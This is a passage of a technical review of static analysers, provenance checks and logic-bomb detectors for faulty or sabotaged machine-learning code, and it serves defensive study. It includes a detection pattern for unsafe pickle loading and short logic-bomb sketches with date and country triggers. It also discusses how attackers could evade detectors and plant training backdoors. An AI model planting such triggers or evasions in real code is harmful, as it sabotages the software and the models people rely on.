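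The tool also reports *overlap leakage*, where the same rows appear in training and testing, and *multi-test leakage*, where a notebook evaluates models on the same data repeatedly and has no fresh test data left. It can only estimate whether two datasets share rows, and it normally treats a split as correct, so it misses the overlap if one set contains rows 0 to 99 and the other starts at row 50. Its developers accepted this because the mistake is very rare, but someone who wanted to inflate a score could choose such a split deliberately.

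The researchers tested the tool on 100 notebooks they labelled by hand. It ran on 94 of them and reported 41 problems, of which 40 were real, a precision of 97.6%. It found 40 of the 59 real problems, a recall of 67.8%. Unsupported libraries caused about a third of the misses. The researchers' own labels were wrong in seven notebooks, so even experts overlook leakage.

They then ran the tool on 107,603 GitHub notebooks and got a warning for 29.6% of them. The rate was lower for tutorials (16.2%) and popular notebooks (20.9%), but still high for code that others are likely to copy. Some warnings about multi-test leakage may be wrong because the developer kept separate test data outside the notebook. *LeakageDetector 2.0* (2025) describes an extension that brings the tool to Visual Studio Code, where it finds leakage in notebooks and suggests corrections.

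### Faults spread over several files

Larger projects divide the work among files, and each file can look correct by itself. *Beyond Local Patterns*, by Mahmoudi, Moha and colleagues, gives an example with three files. One defines a function that rescales data using averages over all rows, another defines a function that splits off a test set, and the main script calls them in that order. This causes leakage because the test rows influence the averages, but a tool has to analyse all three files together to detect it.

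The analyser SpecDetect4ML looks for 22 "code smells", patterns that often indicate a problem in machine-learning code. Examples include leakage, uncontrolled randomness and gradients that the program does not clear, as when line 6 is missing from the ten-line training loop. The developers write each smell as a short logical rule. One rule, for instance, matches any call to a machine-learning method that does not state its settings explicitly. The tool builds a code property graph for each file, then links the files using an index of the project's imports, renamed functions and calls. A rule can therefore check whether the program rescaled data before splitting it, even if the calls are in different places.

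The same rules can also run on syntax trees alone, so the researchers could measure how much the graphs help. Six people with machine-learning experience labelled 2,547 smells in ten software projects without seeing the tool's output. With syntax trees, the tool found 68.62% of them, and with the graphs it found 88.14%. Precision, which the team estimated from a separate sample of alerts, was about 90% either way. The improvement came mostly from faults that involve several functions or files:

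| Where the deciding evidence is | Labelled smells | Found with syntax trees | Found with graphs |
|---|---|---|---|
| One statement | 383 | 353 | 353 |
| Order of statements in one file | 1,221 | 1,173 | 1,173 |
| Several functions in one file | 607 | 205 | 594 |
| Several files | 94 | 17 | 81 |
| Configuration values | 132 | 0 | 44 |
| Behaviour at run time | 110 | 0 | 0 |

The overall figures combine smells that differ widely in how often they occur and how well the tool detects them. Uncontrolled randomness, usually a missing random seed, makes up nearly half of the labelled cases. Only four cases involve leakage, and the tool found three of them but raised six false alarms. It did much better on uncleared gradients, finding 60 of 63 cases with three false alarms. Mahmoudi and colleagues note that code that deliberately adds up gradients over several batches can trigger this rule.

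SpecDetect4ML reported 134,460 smells across 890 projects totalling more than 20 million lines of code, with at least one in 93% of the projects. The researchers treat these reports as places to review rather than confirmed defects.

Three language models were also given the 22 descriptions. Qwen 3 30B Instruct found 48% of the labelled smells, Claude Sonnet 4.6 found 38% and DeepSeek V4 Flash found 29%, all with precision close to SpecDetect4ML's. Each model had one attempt and saw only short pieces of code, so a model that could search the whole repository would probably find more.

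Sometimes an analyser has to look at the data to tell whether the code is faulty. A support vector machine, a common kind of classifier, can perform badly if one column of its data ranges from 0 to 1 and another from 0 to 10,000, so whether a script needs to rescale its data before training depends on what is in the data file. The analyser in *Data-aware Static Analysis* (Meijer, Sandahl and Varró, 2026) therefore opens the file. It traces the data back from the training call to the line that loads it, reads a sample, and checks the sample against a written "contract" for the model. If the script transforms the data along the way, the analyser uses rules about what each transformation guarantees, so it never has to run the script. Checks that run during training can test similar assumptions, but they report a fault only once the computation has started.

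The prototype found faults in 5 of 21 notebooks from Kaggle, a website that hosts data-science competitions. Seven of its 17 warnings depended on the data, and all seven concerned one notebook. Two of these seven were wrong because the tool's sample contained no missing values, so it flagged the code that filled them in as unnecessary. The test shows that the method can work, but it has too few cases to show how often.

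### Rules written for machine-learning libraries

A team that does not want to build its own analyser can write rules for an existing one. Semgrep is a popular tool that searches code for patterns which themselves look like code. The security company Trail of Bits published 11 rules for machine-learning libraries, which it describes in *Secure your machine learning with Semgrep*. One of them concerns NumPy, Python's standard library for arrays. NumPy can load pickle files, which can run code, but only if the caller turns this option on. The rule searches for

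`numpy.load(..., allow_pickle=$VALUE)`

Here `...` stands for any other arguments and `$VALUE` for whatever the programmer wrote. A second condition requires `$VALUE` to be `True` or a positive whole number, because Python treats such numbers as true. The rule catches `allow_pickle=1` and ignores `allow_pickle=False`. It would miss `allow_pickle=config.allow_pickle`, because the value is in a settings file and the rule checks only the text of the call.

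Another rule covers a mistake with random numbers. Programs that train on images often crop or rotate each picture at random, using several worker processes in parallel. In some versions of PyTorch, every worker started with the same state of NumPy's random-number generator, so they all made the same changes. The rule flags a dataset class that calls NumPy's `randint` function when it fetches an item. It does not list NumPy's other random functions, so it would miss the same mistake made with one of those.

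Trail of Bits also mentions an attack by Ilia Shumailov and colleagues that controls the order of a model's training data to stop the model from learning or to insert a backdoor. Faulty randomness in a data loader could therefore be an accident or an attack. The `randint` rule does not distinguish between the two, and it covers only one kind of randomness error.

### How often honest code sets off an alarm

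In *Shifting Left for Machine Learning*, Bhuiyan, Prowell and colleagues ran the scanner Bandit on 278 open-source projects that train models from labelled examples. They removed alerts they judged false and sorted the rest into 22 types of security weakness. This left 3,964 weaknesses in 2,982 of the 36,022 scripts, or about 8% of scripts. A third of the weaknesses were calls to "potentially dangerous" functions, such as those that load pickle files.

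The count probably overstates the danger. The researchers included every potentially dangerous function without checking whether the code used it unsafely. They also counted each hard-coded password under two types, which adds 110 to the total. Some of their published examples look harmless. One "password" is a variable with `TOKEN` in its name that holds the marker language models use for an unknown word. Another line, listed as an example of weak random numbers, appears to pick colours for different classes of object. Weak random numbers are a problem when generating encryption keys. Bandit's rules suit a web server that handles passwords, but in machine-learning code "token" usually means a piece of text, and most random numbers have nothing to do with encryption.

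In a much larger survey, NVIDIA's security team examined about 3.5 million Python files and notebooks that users had run on Kaggle between April 2020 and August 2023, many of them successive versions of the same work. It used 162 Semgrep rules, including those from Trail of Bits, and TruffleHog, a tool that finds access keys and checks whether they still work. The team found more than 140 working keys for services such as OpenAI and Amazon's cloud, and over 45,000 places where the code loaded pickle files through common libraries.

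The team found little sign of malice. Google's Safe Browsing service did not link any web addresses in the code to malware, and the team saw no files loaded from sources that would be easy to hijack. The Safe Browsing check would miss an attack that used an address not yet known to Google, but it supports the view that most of these pickle loads were ordinary. A rule that treats pickle loading as a sign of an attack would produce a huge number of false alarms on this kind of code.

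A few of the Kaggle notebooks tried to import `panda` or `mathplotlib` instead of `pandas` and `matplotlib`. Attackers publish malicious packages under misspelled names like these, so a researcher's typing error can bring in foreign code. NVIDIA's similar analysis of more than 300 highly ranked machine-learning repositories on GitHub found the same range of problems, although the company had expected GitHub projects to be somewhat safer than Kaggle notebooks, which are mostly quick experiments.

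### General analysers on the libraries themselves

The surveys above covered code that uses machine-learning libraries. The libraries themselves contain a lot of C++, a compiled language in which memory errors are common. For *Automatic Static Vulnerability Detection for Machine Learning Libraries*, Shiri Harzevili, Shin and colleagues collected 410 faults that developers had fixed in TensorFlow, PyTorch, MXNet and Mlpack. They ran five general analysers on the code from before each fix and checked whether any warning matched the fault.

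The tools found five of the 410, or 1.2%. (The paper gives the rate as 0.01%, an arithmetic error, and one of its summaries gives the count as four.) Only Flawfinder and RATS, which search for the names of risky functions, found any. The Clang static analyzer, Cppcheck and Infer, which analyse the code in more depth, found none. The paper cites an earlier study of 27 ordinary software projects in which analysers found between 20% and 53% of known vulnerabilities. The gap is large, but the comparison is rough because the two studies used different faults and methods.

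The researchers' explanation is that the tools do not account for the libraries' own rules. In one TensorFlow fault, a function reads the third dimension of a tensor without checking that the tensor has three dimensions. The code contains no risky function, so to detect the fault, a tool needs information about what input the function requires and has to trace where that input comes from. Detecting a memory leak in Mlpack similarly requires the information that `CleanMemory()` releases memory.

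Phoenix, presented in *Rise From The Ashes* (Yang, Lin and colleagues, July 2026), does better by letting a language model work out such rules. It checks whether facts about a tensor remain correct as the tensor passes between PyTorch's Python, C++ and graphics-processor code. Ariadne and PyTea did something similar for users' programs. Phoenix starts from 40 past PyTorch fixes and 16 general types of weakness. For each, a language model (GPT-5.4 in the tests) summarises the pattern and names a function to examine. The tool retrieves the real code, and the model writes a structured record of what passes from one part to another, including the tensor's shape, data type and device. Finally, the model looks for a requirement that one side relies on but the other does not guarantee.

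One of the bugs it found was in the gradient code for a three-dimensional averaging operation. To find the data for item n in a batch, the program should skip n × depth × height × width × channels numbers, but the code left out the depth. It could run without crashing and read gradients from the wrong part of the batch, which would spoil the training.

Phoenix raised 36 alarms on PyTorch, of which 31 were real bugs. PyTorch's maintainers have confirmed 26 and accepted fixes for 20. On the same code, Bandit raised 172 alarms, of which one was a real bug, and the Clang analyser raised 218, none of which were real bugs. Retrieving the real code was essential, because 26 of the model's 43 alarms were false when it wrote its records from the bug descriptions alone.

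Phoenix's recall is unknown because nobody knows how many bugs remain in PyTorch. However, two testing tools that generate and run programs found 20 bugs between them, and Phoenix found only one of those.

### When the fault is deliberate

Many of these tools work by checking rules that apply whatever a project is for. For example, the inner dimensions of two multiplied matrices must match, and test data must not influence training. The tools can detect sabotage that breaks such a rule as easily as an accidental mistake. If an attacker deleted line 6 from the training loop, SpecDetect4ML would probably flag the omission, as it does when a developer forgets the line. Similarly, an attacker who removed the depth from PyTorch's gradient calculation would create the same bug that Phoenix found.

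The yellow-square attack breaks none of these rules. Its shapes match, its steps are in the right order, it uses no test data and it calls no dangerous function.

Attacks that use a flagged function are hard to pick out from ordinary code. If a malicious script that loaded its payload from a pickle file were added to the collection studied by Bhuiyan and colleagues, it would be one of 2,983 flagged scripts, even after people had removed the alerts they considered false.

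Recall on accidental bugs is also a poor guide to recall on deliberately hidden code, because an attacker can choose where to put the evidence. SpecDetect4ML's 88% recall is an average over mistakes that nobody was trying to hide. It found only a third of the smells that depended on configuration values and none of those that appeared only at run time. Its developers also list features it does not handle reliably, including `eval`, `exec` and code that replaces functions while the program runs. An attacker can use that list to evade the tool, or run the tool and rewrite the code until the warning disappears.

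None of these tests included code known to be malicious. The labels recorded whether the code was faulty, not why, and a correct warning may not show whether the fault was deliberate. Yang and colleagues point out that developers may have a reason to inflate a model's accuracy when a contract or competition depends on it. Their tool would give the same warning whether a developer let test data into training deliberately, to win the contract, or accidentally, by putting two lines in the wrong order.

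## Experiments on recognising code that came from elsewhere

Detectors can also look for planted code by checking where it came from. A malicious line can have matching tensor shapes and call no dangerous function, yet be missing from the project's public source or fit badly with the code around it. Researchers have built detectors that look for each of these signs, mostly in general software. Several of the studies that compare releases with their source used Python packages, but none of the studies below was designed to test machine-learning projects.

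### Signed build records

Most Python projects get their dependencies from the Python Package Index (PyPI), a public registry. Developers usually keep a package's source in a GitHub repository, build a release from it and upload the release to PyPI. Users install that release, and PyPI does not require it to match the repository.

Many projects now use an automated workflow to upload their releases. Under PyPI's *trusted publishing*, a project names the workflow that may publish for it, such as the file `release.yml` in a specific GitHub repository. According to Trail of Bits' *Attestations* (2024), this also produces provenance, meaning claims about the repository and workflow at the moment of publication. PyPI can attach an *attestation*, a signed statement that anyone can check, to the release. A user can then verify that the release came through a trusted publisher, as deps.dev's *Introducing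 PyPI digital attestation support* explains.

This helps most when an attacker uploads a hijacked release directly to PyPI, because that release lacks the usual attestation. A lock file, which lists the exact versions a project installs, can also record attestation data. In snarky.ca's *Why pylock.toml includes digital attestations*, a Python developer argues that if the project hit by one real attack of this kind had published attestations, users with such a file would have noticed something odd.

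Most packages have no attestation to check. PyPI (2025) reported that 17% of uploads in the preceding year included one. *Reproducibility is Not Enough* (Solarin, Kalu and colleagues, 2026) counted packages instead of uploads in PyPI and three other registries, and found attestations for only 2.0% to 6.6%. A missing attestation is therefore a useful warning only for a project that normally has them. A valid attestation, like a valid signature, does not rule out a compromised build system.

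### Comparing a release with its repository

Without an attestation, a reviewer can still compare the release with the public source. Vu, Massacci and colleagues (2021), in *LastPyMile*, did this for popular PyPI packages. They call a file or line a *phantom* if it is in the release but was never in the repository. Their tool finds phantoms in three steps:

1. It goes through every commit on every branch of the repository, computes a hash of each file (a short fingerprint of its contents), and stores the hashes and the individual lines.
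2. It does the same for the files in the release.
3. It reports each release file whose hash is not among the stored ones, and then the lines in that file that the repository never contained.

Because the tool uses the whole history, it does not have to work out which commit a release came from. But it would report no phantom if an attacker restored an old version of a file with a security hole that the developers have since closed, because the old file's hash is in the history.

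Vu and colleagues applied the method to 93,252 release files from 2,438 packages. About 65% of them differed from the repository, so a difference alone does not indicate an attack. Only 5.8% differed in a Python file. Build tools cause many of these differences by writing version numbers into files such as `setup.py`. Developers cause others by generating code automatically or patching a release by hand. The researchers traced 66 cases with more than 1,000 differing files to developers moving code between repositories.

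The comparison is more useful as a filter for another scanner. Vu and colleagues ran Bandit, with extra rules for suspicious calls, on three legitimate packages and three malicious imitations of them. They then kept only the alerts on phantom lines:

| Release | Malicious | All Bandit alerts | Alerts on phantom lines |
|---|---|---|---|
| urllib3 1.26.3 | no | 1,398 | 0 |
| requests 2.25.1 | no | 505 | 0 |
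| setuptools 53.0.0 | no | 762 | 0 |
| urlib3 1.21.1 | yes | 1,044 | 12 |
| request 1.0.117 | yes | 27 | 20 |
| setup-tools 36.0.1 | yes | 489 | 12 |

Without the filter, each legitimate package set off more alerts than its malicious imitation, but the filter removed all the alerts for the legitimate packages. Six packages are far too few to estimate a false positive rate, and the malicious ones were fairly easy to detect. `urlib3`, for example, listed the real urllib3 repository as its source, so the added code stood out. An attacker could link to a repository that already contains the malicious code, and the comparison would find nothing.

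A reviewer also needs the right repository. The metadata search in *PyRadar* (2024) retrieved repository information for 72.1% of PyPI releases. *Software Supply Chain Smells* (2026) treats a missing or broken source link as a warning sign, citing a malicious release of the PyPI package `ctx` that people detected with the help of the linked source code. But this warning would be common, since Solarin and colleagues found no valid repository address for 14.7% to 42.4% of packages, depending on the registry.

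### Building the release again

A stricter check rebuilds the release from its source and compares the two copies byte by byte. *No Snake Oil* (Dietrich, White and colleagues, 2026) tested this on 10,449 releases of popular Python packages, using two rebuilding tools. Macaron built 68.0% of the releases and OSS Rebuild built 56.5%. Only 15.4% of Macaron's builds and 19.1% of OSS Rebuild's were identical to the copy on PyPI, so flagging every mismatch would flag most legitimate software.

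Many mismatches are trivial. A *wheel*, the ready-to-install form of a Python package, contains one file that records the build tool and its version, and another that lists a hash for every other file. A new version of the build tool therefore changes both. Dietrich and colleagues' program, daleq4py, uses explicit rules to remove such differences before it compares two wheels. In Python files it ignores comments and formatting but treats any other change as real.

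Dietrich and colleagues applied daleq4py to the rebuilds that had started from matching Python source. It classified 60.2% of Macaron's rebuilds and 78.9% of OSS Rebuild's as equivalent to the published wheel. Someone would still have to examine the remaining 2,372 and 1,167 releases, respectively, and the researchers do not report finding an attack among them.

Such rules need care because an attacker can hide code in whatever the comparison ignores. Solarin and colleagues define several levels of equivalence, from identical bytes to identical code. Their code-level comparison tolerates differences in a generated file called `_version.py`. That file normally holds little more than a version number, but Python can run it like any other Python file, so a checker has to inspect any changes to it.

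A rebuild also needs the exact commit, and even an attestation may point to the wrong one. For version 1.5.2 of freezegun, a testing library, the attestation identified the commit that had started the release process, but a later commit changed the version number. Macaron used the attested commit and therefore built version 1.5.1.

Dietrich and colleagues left out 1,731 releases with compiled components because neither tool builds them. The results therefore do not cover PyTorch or NumPy, which have such components and do most of the computation in a training loop. Among the remaining releases, the failed rebuilds included versions of MMDetection, an object-detection library, and of LiteLLM, whose build pipeline attackers had compromised earlier in the year.

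A confirmed mismatch in executable code proves that the release contains something its public source does not account for, but not who added it or why. A match proves only that the release corresponds to that source. If the engineer's yellow-square condition is in the repository, every correct rebuild will include it. A rebuild can also reproduce the effect of a poisoned build tool if it uses the same tool.

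### How predictable a line is

Malicious code already in the repository needs a different test, and one option is to measure how predictable the code is. Programmers repeat themselves a lot, so a statistical model trained on existing code can often predict the next *token* (a name, symbol or number). A line that the model predicts poorly may be out of place.

The usual measure is *cross-entropy*. For a sequence of N tokens, it is

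H = −(1/N) Σ log₂ P(tᵢ | hᵢ)

Here P(tᵢ | hᵢ) is the probability the model assigns to token tᵢ given its context hᵢ. A token with probability 1/2 contributes 1 bit, one with probability 1/4 contributes 2 bits, and one with probability 1 contributes 0 bits.

Line 6 of the training loop, `optimizer.zero_grad()`, has five tokens: `optimizer`, the dot, `zero_grad` and the two brackets. Suppose a model gives them probabilities of 1/4, 1, 1/2, 1 and 1. They contribute 2 + 0 + 1 + 0 + 0 = 3 bits, so H is 3/5, or 0.6 bits per token. If someone replaced `zero_grad` with a name that the model gives a probability of 1/1,024, that token would contribute 10 bits and H would rise to 2.4. If a saboteur deleted the line, it would have no tokens to score.

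In *On the "Naturalness" of Buggy Code*, Ray, Hellendoorn and colleagues (2015) used 8,296 bug fixes from ten Java projects to test whether faulty lines have higher cross-entropy than other lines. They counted a line as faulty if a fix removed it. Their model estimated each token's probability from the few tokens next to it, and combined counts from the rest of the project with counts from the same file.

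Faulty lines averaged about 0.8 bits more than other lines. When the fix removed at most two lines, the difference was about 1.7 bits. In one example from Netty, a networking library, a developer had called `setSuccess` although the same file used `trySuccess` in similar places. The faulty line scored 5.96 bits and the corrected one 1.34.

A bug can also have lower entropy than its fix. In another case, a developer copied a line that used `maxChunkSize` and forgot to change the variable's name. The same text already existed elsewhere, so the faulty line scored as ordinary, and correcting it raised the entropy by 5.75 bits. This is a weakness in a tool meant to detect foreign code, because code copied from a popular library is among the most predictable.

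The raw entropy scores were only modestly useful for guiding reviewers. Checking the 5% of lines with the highest entropy was 17% better than checking lines at random, by a measure that weighs bugs found against lines read. Ray and colleagues then adjusted the scores for the type of statement and for how often that type had contained bugs in the past, which raised the result to more than twice that of random checking.

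*CODEBERT-NT* (Khanfir, Jimenez and colleagues, 2022) later used a larger language model, CodeBERT, trained on code from more than six million GitHub projects. CodeBERT ranked faulty Java lines slightly better than simpler models trained on the project being checked, which suggests that the method can work on a project with little history.

Wang, Liu and colleagues (2024), in *ANVIL*, mask a whole line at a time. Their tool removes the line, gives a language model the surrounding code (usually the rest of the function), and has it fill the gap. It then compares the model's line with the original. Cross-entropy alone can miss a small but important difference. If the original is `if(a>=0)` and the model expects `if(a>0)`, most of the line agrees and the average stays low, yet the extra character might let the program read outside an array. The tool therefore adds up four scores:

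δ_hybrid = δ_loss + δ_EM + δ_var + δ_ast

- δ_loss is the average cross-entropy of the original line.
- δ_EM makes the line less suspicious if the model reproduced it exactly.
- δ_var depends on how the model spreads its probability over candidates for the first token. Faulty lines tended to fall in the middle, where the model neither strongly prefers one token nor treats many as equally likely.
- δ_ast counts the nodes in the line's syntax tree, because complicated lines may be more likely to contain mistakes.

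Wang and colleagues tested ANVIL on C and C++ code with known security flaws. Its AUROC was 0.618 on PrimeVul, a collection drawn from more than 700 projects, and 0.686 on flaws published after the model's training data ends. Three detectors trained on labelled examples scored about 0.5 on PrimeVul, which is no better than guessing. Within functions known to be faulty, ANVIL ranked a faulty line in its top three in 31.3% of cases.

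An AUROC of 0.686 is better than chance but far from practical. The test with newer flaws had 235 faulty lines among about 112,000, so a threshold low enough to catch most of them would produce too many false alarms for a reviewer to check. Wang and colleagues call such tools potentially impractical on their own. ANVIL was more useful when they used it to choose starting inputs for fuzzers, which run software on huge numbers of generated inputs to find bugs. With those starting inputs, the fuzzers found 9.4% more bugs in 24 hours.

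All of these experiments used accidental faults in Java, C or C++. ANVIL's results also came from CodeLlama-13B, which is small and old by the standards of late 2026. A stronger model would predict ordinary lines better, but it is not clear how much that would help with machine-learning research, where the line that implements a paper's new idea, such as a loss function, may be the least predictable one in the repository. An attacker can also have a language model write the malicious code, which would probably make it predictable to similar models.

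### Whether the code fits its function

A line of code can be common in general but wrong for its place. Many programs read a password file, but a function that computes a loss has no reason to. A function has high *cohesion* if all of its parts serve one purpose. *Leveraging Code Cohesion Analysis to Identify Source Code Supply Chain Attacks* (Reuben, Mendel and colleagues, 2025) measures cohesion by hiding a function's name and testing how easily a language model can guess it from the code, with an easier guess meaning higher cohesion.

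Names consist of one or more tokens, so the tool tries every length n from one to eight. For each length, it combines the probabilities p₁ … pₙ of the model's best guesses into a harmonic mean, and then keeps the highest result:

Confidence(f, n) = n / (1/p₁ + … + 1/pₙ)

NPC(f) = the largest Confidence(f, n) for n = 1 to 8

Name-prediction-based cohesion (NPC) uses the harmonic mean of token probabilities, which is low if any token has a low probability. For two tokens with probabilities of 0.9 and 0.1, the harmonic mean is 0.18, whereas the ordinary average is 0.5. If someone adds code that steals passwords to a function called `compute_loss`, no short name describes both jobs well, so the NPC should fall.

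Reuben and colleagues studied 54,707 functions from 369 open-source C++ projects. They inserted nine snippets of known malware, about six lines long on average, at the beginning, middle or end of functions. For comparison, they measured how the NPC changed in 425,290 ordinary edits from the projects' histories.

Ordinary edits lowered the NPC by 0.0005 on average, and inserted malware lowered it by 0.027 to 0.040, depending on its position. The difference is statistically significant but much smaller than the variation between functions, with standard deviations of 0.12 for ordinary edits and about 0.2 for malware. The researchers therefore also compared each drop with the usual drop for functions that start with a similar NPC. In a separate analysis, they kept only the roughly 63% of functions with an NPC above 0.5.

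They then ranked all the changes by suspicion and calculated *precision at 100*, the share of the 100 most suspicious functions that contained malware. The table gives the best result from their four ranking methods.

| Malicious to legitimate changes | All functions | Functions with an NPC above 0.5 |
|---|---|---|
| 1 : 100 | 3.41% | 100% |
| 1 : 1,000 | 0.35% | 36.41% |
| 1 : 10,000 | 0.08% | 12.47% |

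At the ratio in the bottom row, only 30 of the functions with an NPC above 0.5 contained malware, so even a perfect detector could put no more than 30 in its top 100. The researchers divided the precision by this maximum, so a score of 12.47% means about four real hits in a list of 100. That would still be a good result for something so rare, since 100 functions picked at random would contain a malicious one only about once in 100 tries. For all functions together, the score of 0.08% means one real hit in every 25 to 30 lists of 100.

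The gap between the columns is hard to explain. A function with an NPC of 0.5 or less cannot fall by more than 0.5, so the largest drops should come from high-scoring functions anyway. Yet when the researchers ranked changes by the size of the drop alone, at a ratio of 1:100, precision was 82.21% for high-scoring functions and 1.41% for all functions. The paper does not explain this difference, and the results for high-scoring functions deserve caution until somebody replicates them.

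The inserted malware was also crude, because nobody adapted it to the surrounding function. A real attacker could put the code in its own function with a fitting name, such as `upload_diagnostics`. Reuben and colleagues acknowledge that real attacks may be more sophisticated. They also found no concrete evidence of real attacks in the 369 projects, so their figures come entirely from simulated attacks.

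Machine-learning scripts would probably be difficult for this method. A research project's `train` function may load data, log results, save checkpoints and upload them, so its name describes the code only loosely even before anyone tampers with it. Notebook code is often not in functions. Two lines that relabel pictures that contain a yellow square would seem to belong in a function called `prepare_labels`.

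### Who or what wrote the code

*Code stylometry* is the attempt to identify a programmer from habits such as naming, spacing and a preference for certain kinds of loop. A project could use it to check whether a change from a developer's account looks like that developer's work. In *De-anonymizing Programmers via Code Stylometry*, Caliskan-Islam, Harang and colleagues (2015) identified who had written C and C++ programs, from 1,600 candidates, with 94% accuracy, using features that included the structure of the syntax tree. They also showed that the method could be used with Python.

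The programs came from Google Code Jam, a contest in which people solve set problems alone. This makes the task easier than in most projects, where several people edit the same function and automatic formatters remove differences in layout. Style is also easy to fake. In *Misleading Authorship Attribution of Source Code using Adversarial Learning*, Quiring, Maier and Rieck (2019) automatically rewrote programs by 204 programmers without changing what the programs did. The accuracy of two attribution methods fell from over 88% to 1%.

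Other detectors try to tell AI-written code from human code. Suh, Tafreshipour and colleagues (2024), in *An Empirical Study on Automatically Detecting AI-Generated Source Code*, found that existing tools performed poorly and did not generalise well enough for practical use. Their own best model reached an F1 score (which combines precision and recall) of 82.55 out of 100. Such a detector learns patterns from the AI models and programming languages in its training data, so its accuracy can drop on code in other languages or from new models, which appear every few months.

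Even a perfect detector of AI-written code would now be of limited use against attackers, because AI writes much of the ordinary code in many projects and attackers can use the same assistants as other developers. A sudden change of style may mean only that a developer switched assistants or wrote something by hand. It can be a reason to ask about the code, for instance in a project that forbids AI-written contributions, but it is very weak evidence of malice.

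Foreign style is especially common in machine learning because researchers openly copy each other's code. Someone who wants to compare a new method with an older one may start from the older method's repository, so one project can legitimately contain the styles of several research groups. For copied code, finding the original is more useful than detecting foreign style. *Using the Uniqueness of Global Identifiers to Determine the Provenance of Python Software Source Code* (2023) presents a method for this that relies on distinctive names in the code. The researchers tested it on Python packages from Debian, a version of the Linux operating system, trying to match them to the same packages in PyPI.

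They found no match for 21 of the packages, because PyPI's copies lacked some of the original source files. One package had 85 files in Debian and only two in PyPI. A search like this therefore needs a good collection of originals, which for research code would have to include GitHub repositories as well as published packages. A reviewer who finds the original can compare the two versions line by line. If someone copied a clean training script and added a condition that changes certain labels, the comparison would show that condition among the differences.

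## Experiments on finding hidden triggers and unusual control flow

A tool can also look for such a condition directly, without an original to compare against. Hidden code usually runs only under a narrow condition, such as after a certain date, for one password or for one rare kind of picture, so ordinary tests never run it. Researchers have tested detectors for this pattern on phone apps, industrial controllers and general programs such as file servers, but none of the tests below used machine-learning code.

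### What a trigger looks like in a control-flow graph

Fratantonio, Bianchi and colleagues, in *TriggerScope*, describe a navigation app for soldiers that gives misleading directions after a certain date. In Python, it would look roughly like this:

```python
def show_route(now):
    position = read_gps()
    if now > date(2016, 12, 22):
        route = request_long_route(position)
    else:
        route = request_shortest_route(position)
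    display(route)
```

In the control-flow graph, two arrows lead from the condition, one to each request, and the two paths meet again at `display`. A navigation app can legitimately read the phone's location and send it to a server, so a list of sensitive operations or data flows would show nothing odd. However, a network request here depends on how today's date compares with a hard-coded date, which is unusual. TriggerScope, a 2016 analyser for Android apps, therefore examines the condition more closely than the code it guards.

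### TriggerScope's steps

Android apps come as bytecode, a compact set of instructions, in which the date comparison shrinks to a test of whether some number is zero. TriggerScope has to recover its meaning before it can judge it:

1. It uses *symbolic execution*, which works through the program with symbols in place of unknown values. The current time becomes `#now`, so the tool can rewrite the test for zero as "`#now` after 2016/12/22".
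2. For each block of code, it works backwards to the start of the function and collects the conditions on the way. It joins conditions along one path with "and", and joins alternative paths with "or".
3. It simplifies the result. Let p be the date check and q any earlier condition. The two requests run under p ∧ q and ¬p ∧ q. `display` comes after both, so its condition is (p ∧ q) ∨ (¬p ∧ q), which simplifies to q. Without this step, the tool would wrongly treat `display` as dependent on the date.
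4. It marks a condition as suspicious if it compares the current time with a constant, checks for a fixed location, or looks for hard-coded text in a phone message. A game's check that does something every few seconds does not count.
5. It keeps only suspicious conditions that control a sensitive operation. The control can be indirect, as when the guarded code sets a variable that a later condition reads.
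6. It drops comparisons with 0 or −1, which usually just test whether the app has stored a time yet.

Fratantonio and colleagues ran the tool on about 9,300 apps from Google's app store that they considered benign. Each stage of the analysis removed most of the remaining false alarms:

| What the tool flags | Benign apps flagged | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| Any condition on time, location or messages | 1,386 | 14.88% |
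| Only suspicious conditions | 462 | 4.96% |
| Only those that control a sensitive operation | 117 | 1.26% |
| Only those left after the final filter | 35 | 0.38% |

TriggerScope also flagged all 14 malicious apps in the test, but an outside team had written 11 of them for a government research programme, so they may not be typical of real malware. Two of the 35 "benign" apps contained something like a backdoor. One, RemoteLock, unlocked the phone whenever it received a message containing a particular long string. Fratantonio and colleagues still counted both as false positives.

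### A replication with far more false alarms

TriggerScope's developers could not share the tool, so Samhi and Bartel built their own version, TSOpen, from the published description and presented it in *On The (In)Effectiveness of Static Logic Bomb Detection for Android Apps* (2021). They sent their paper to TriggerScope's developers, who saw no significant problem with TSOpen's design.

Samhi and Bartel collected 11,338 benign apps using the original selection rules. TSOpen finished analysing 7,297 of them and flagged 3,099. They report a false positive rate of 27.3%, calculated over all 11,338 apps. TriggerScope's rate of 0.38% was calculated over only the apps it finished analysing, and TSOpen's rate calculated the same way is 42.5%. Ignoring code from common libraries lowered it to 23.3%. In a larger run on 508,122 apps of all kinds, the reported rate ranged from 17.2% to 24.6%, depending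 on how many antivirus engines had to flag an app before it counted as malware.

To explain the gap, the researchers changed one part of the method at a time. The age of the apps, the time limit and the way of building the call graph made little difference, but the list of sensitive operations mattered a lot. Theirs had 12,755 entries, including the function that puts text on the screen, which alone accounted for 12.8% of the detections. Removing the 68 entries that caused the most alarms was enough to reach 0.38%. When they removed entries at random, they had to delete more than 11,500 to get that low, and by then the tool missed between 70% and 95% of a set of malicious apps. (That figure probably overstates the harm, because some of those apps may have contained no logic bomb.)

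Analysing only code in the app's own package also gave about 0.3%. In some apps this ignored more than 93% of the code, and an attacker could escape the check by renaming a package.

None of this fully explains the original result. The list of benign apps from 2016 no longer exists, and the TriggerScope paper does not mention a library filter, although Samhi and Bartel believe TriggerScope must have used one. TSOpen could also contain mistakes, but it found the same logic bombs as TriggerScope in the three malicious apps the original team shared. A developer who builds such a tool from the published description should expect a rate closer to TSOpen's.

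One of TSOpen's false alarms came from card.io, a library that reads payment cards with the phone's camera. Its code keeps trying to open the camera until a time limit passes, so a sensitive operation depends on the clock. TSOpen was more useful for examining individual apps. In a manual review of 200 apps, the researchers used its reports to locate malicious code in less than two minutes on average.

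### Looking for abnormal triggers

Difuzer, the tool for which Samhi and colleagues wrote their definition of a logic bomb, does not need a fixed list of suspicious conditions. It first uses data-flow analysis to find conditions that depend on the phone or its surroundings. Its sources are 1,285 Android functions that return facts such as the network's country or the user's location, and its sinks are the conditions themselves. The underlying analyser accepts only function calls as sinks, so Difuzer inserts a dummy call before each `if`:

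```python
country = get_network_country()
dummy_sink(country, "RU")        # inserted by the tool
if country == "RU":
    run_hidden_code()
```

If a value from a source reaches the dummy call, the condition depends on that value. Difuzer then describes the condition and its guarded code with nine features. Several concern ways of hiding code, such as loading it while the app runs. Others count the functions that the app calls only behind this condition, or record whether the guarded code uses the value that the condition tested. The last feature measures how much the two branches differ:

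D = 1 − |A ∩ B| / |A ∪ B|

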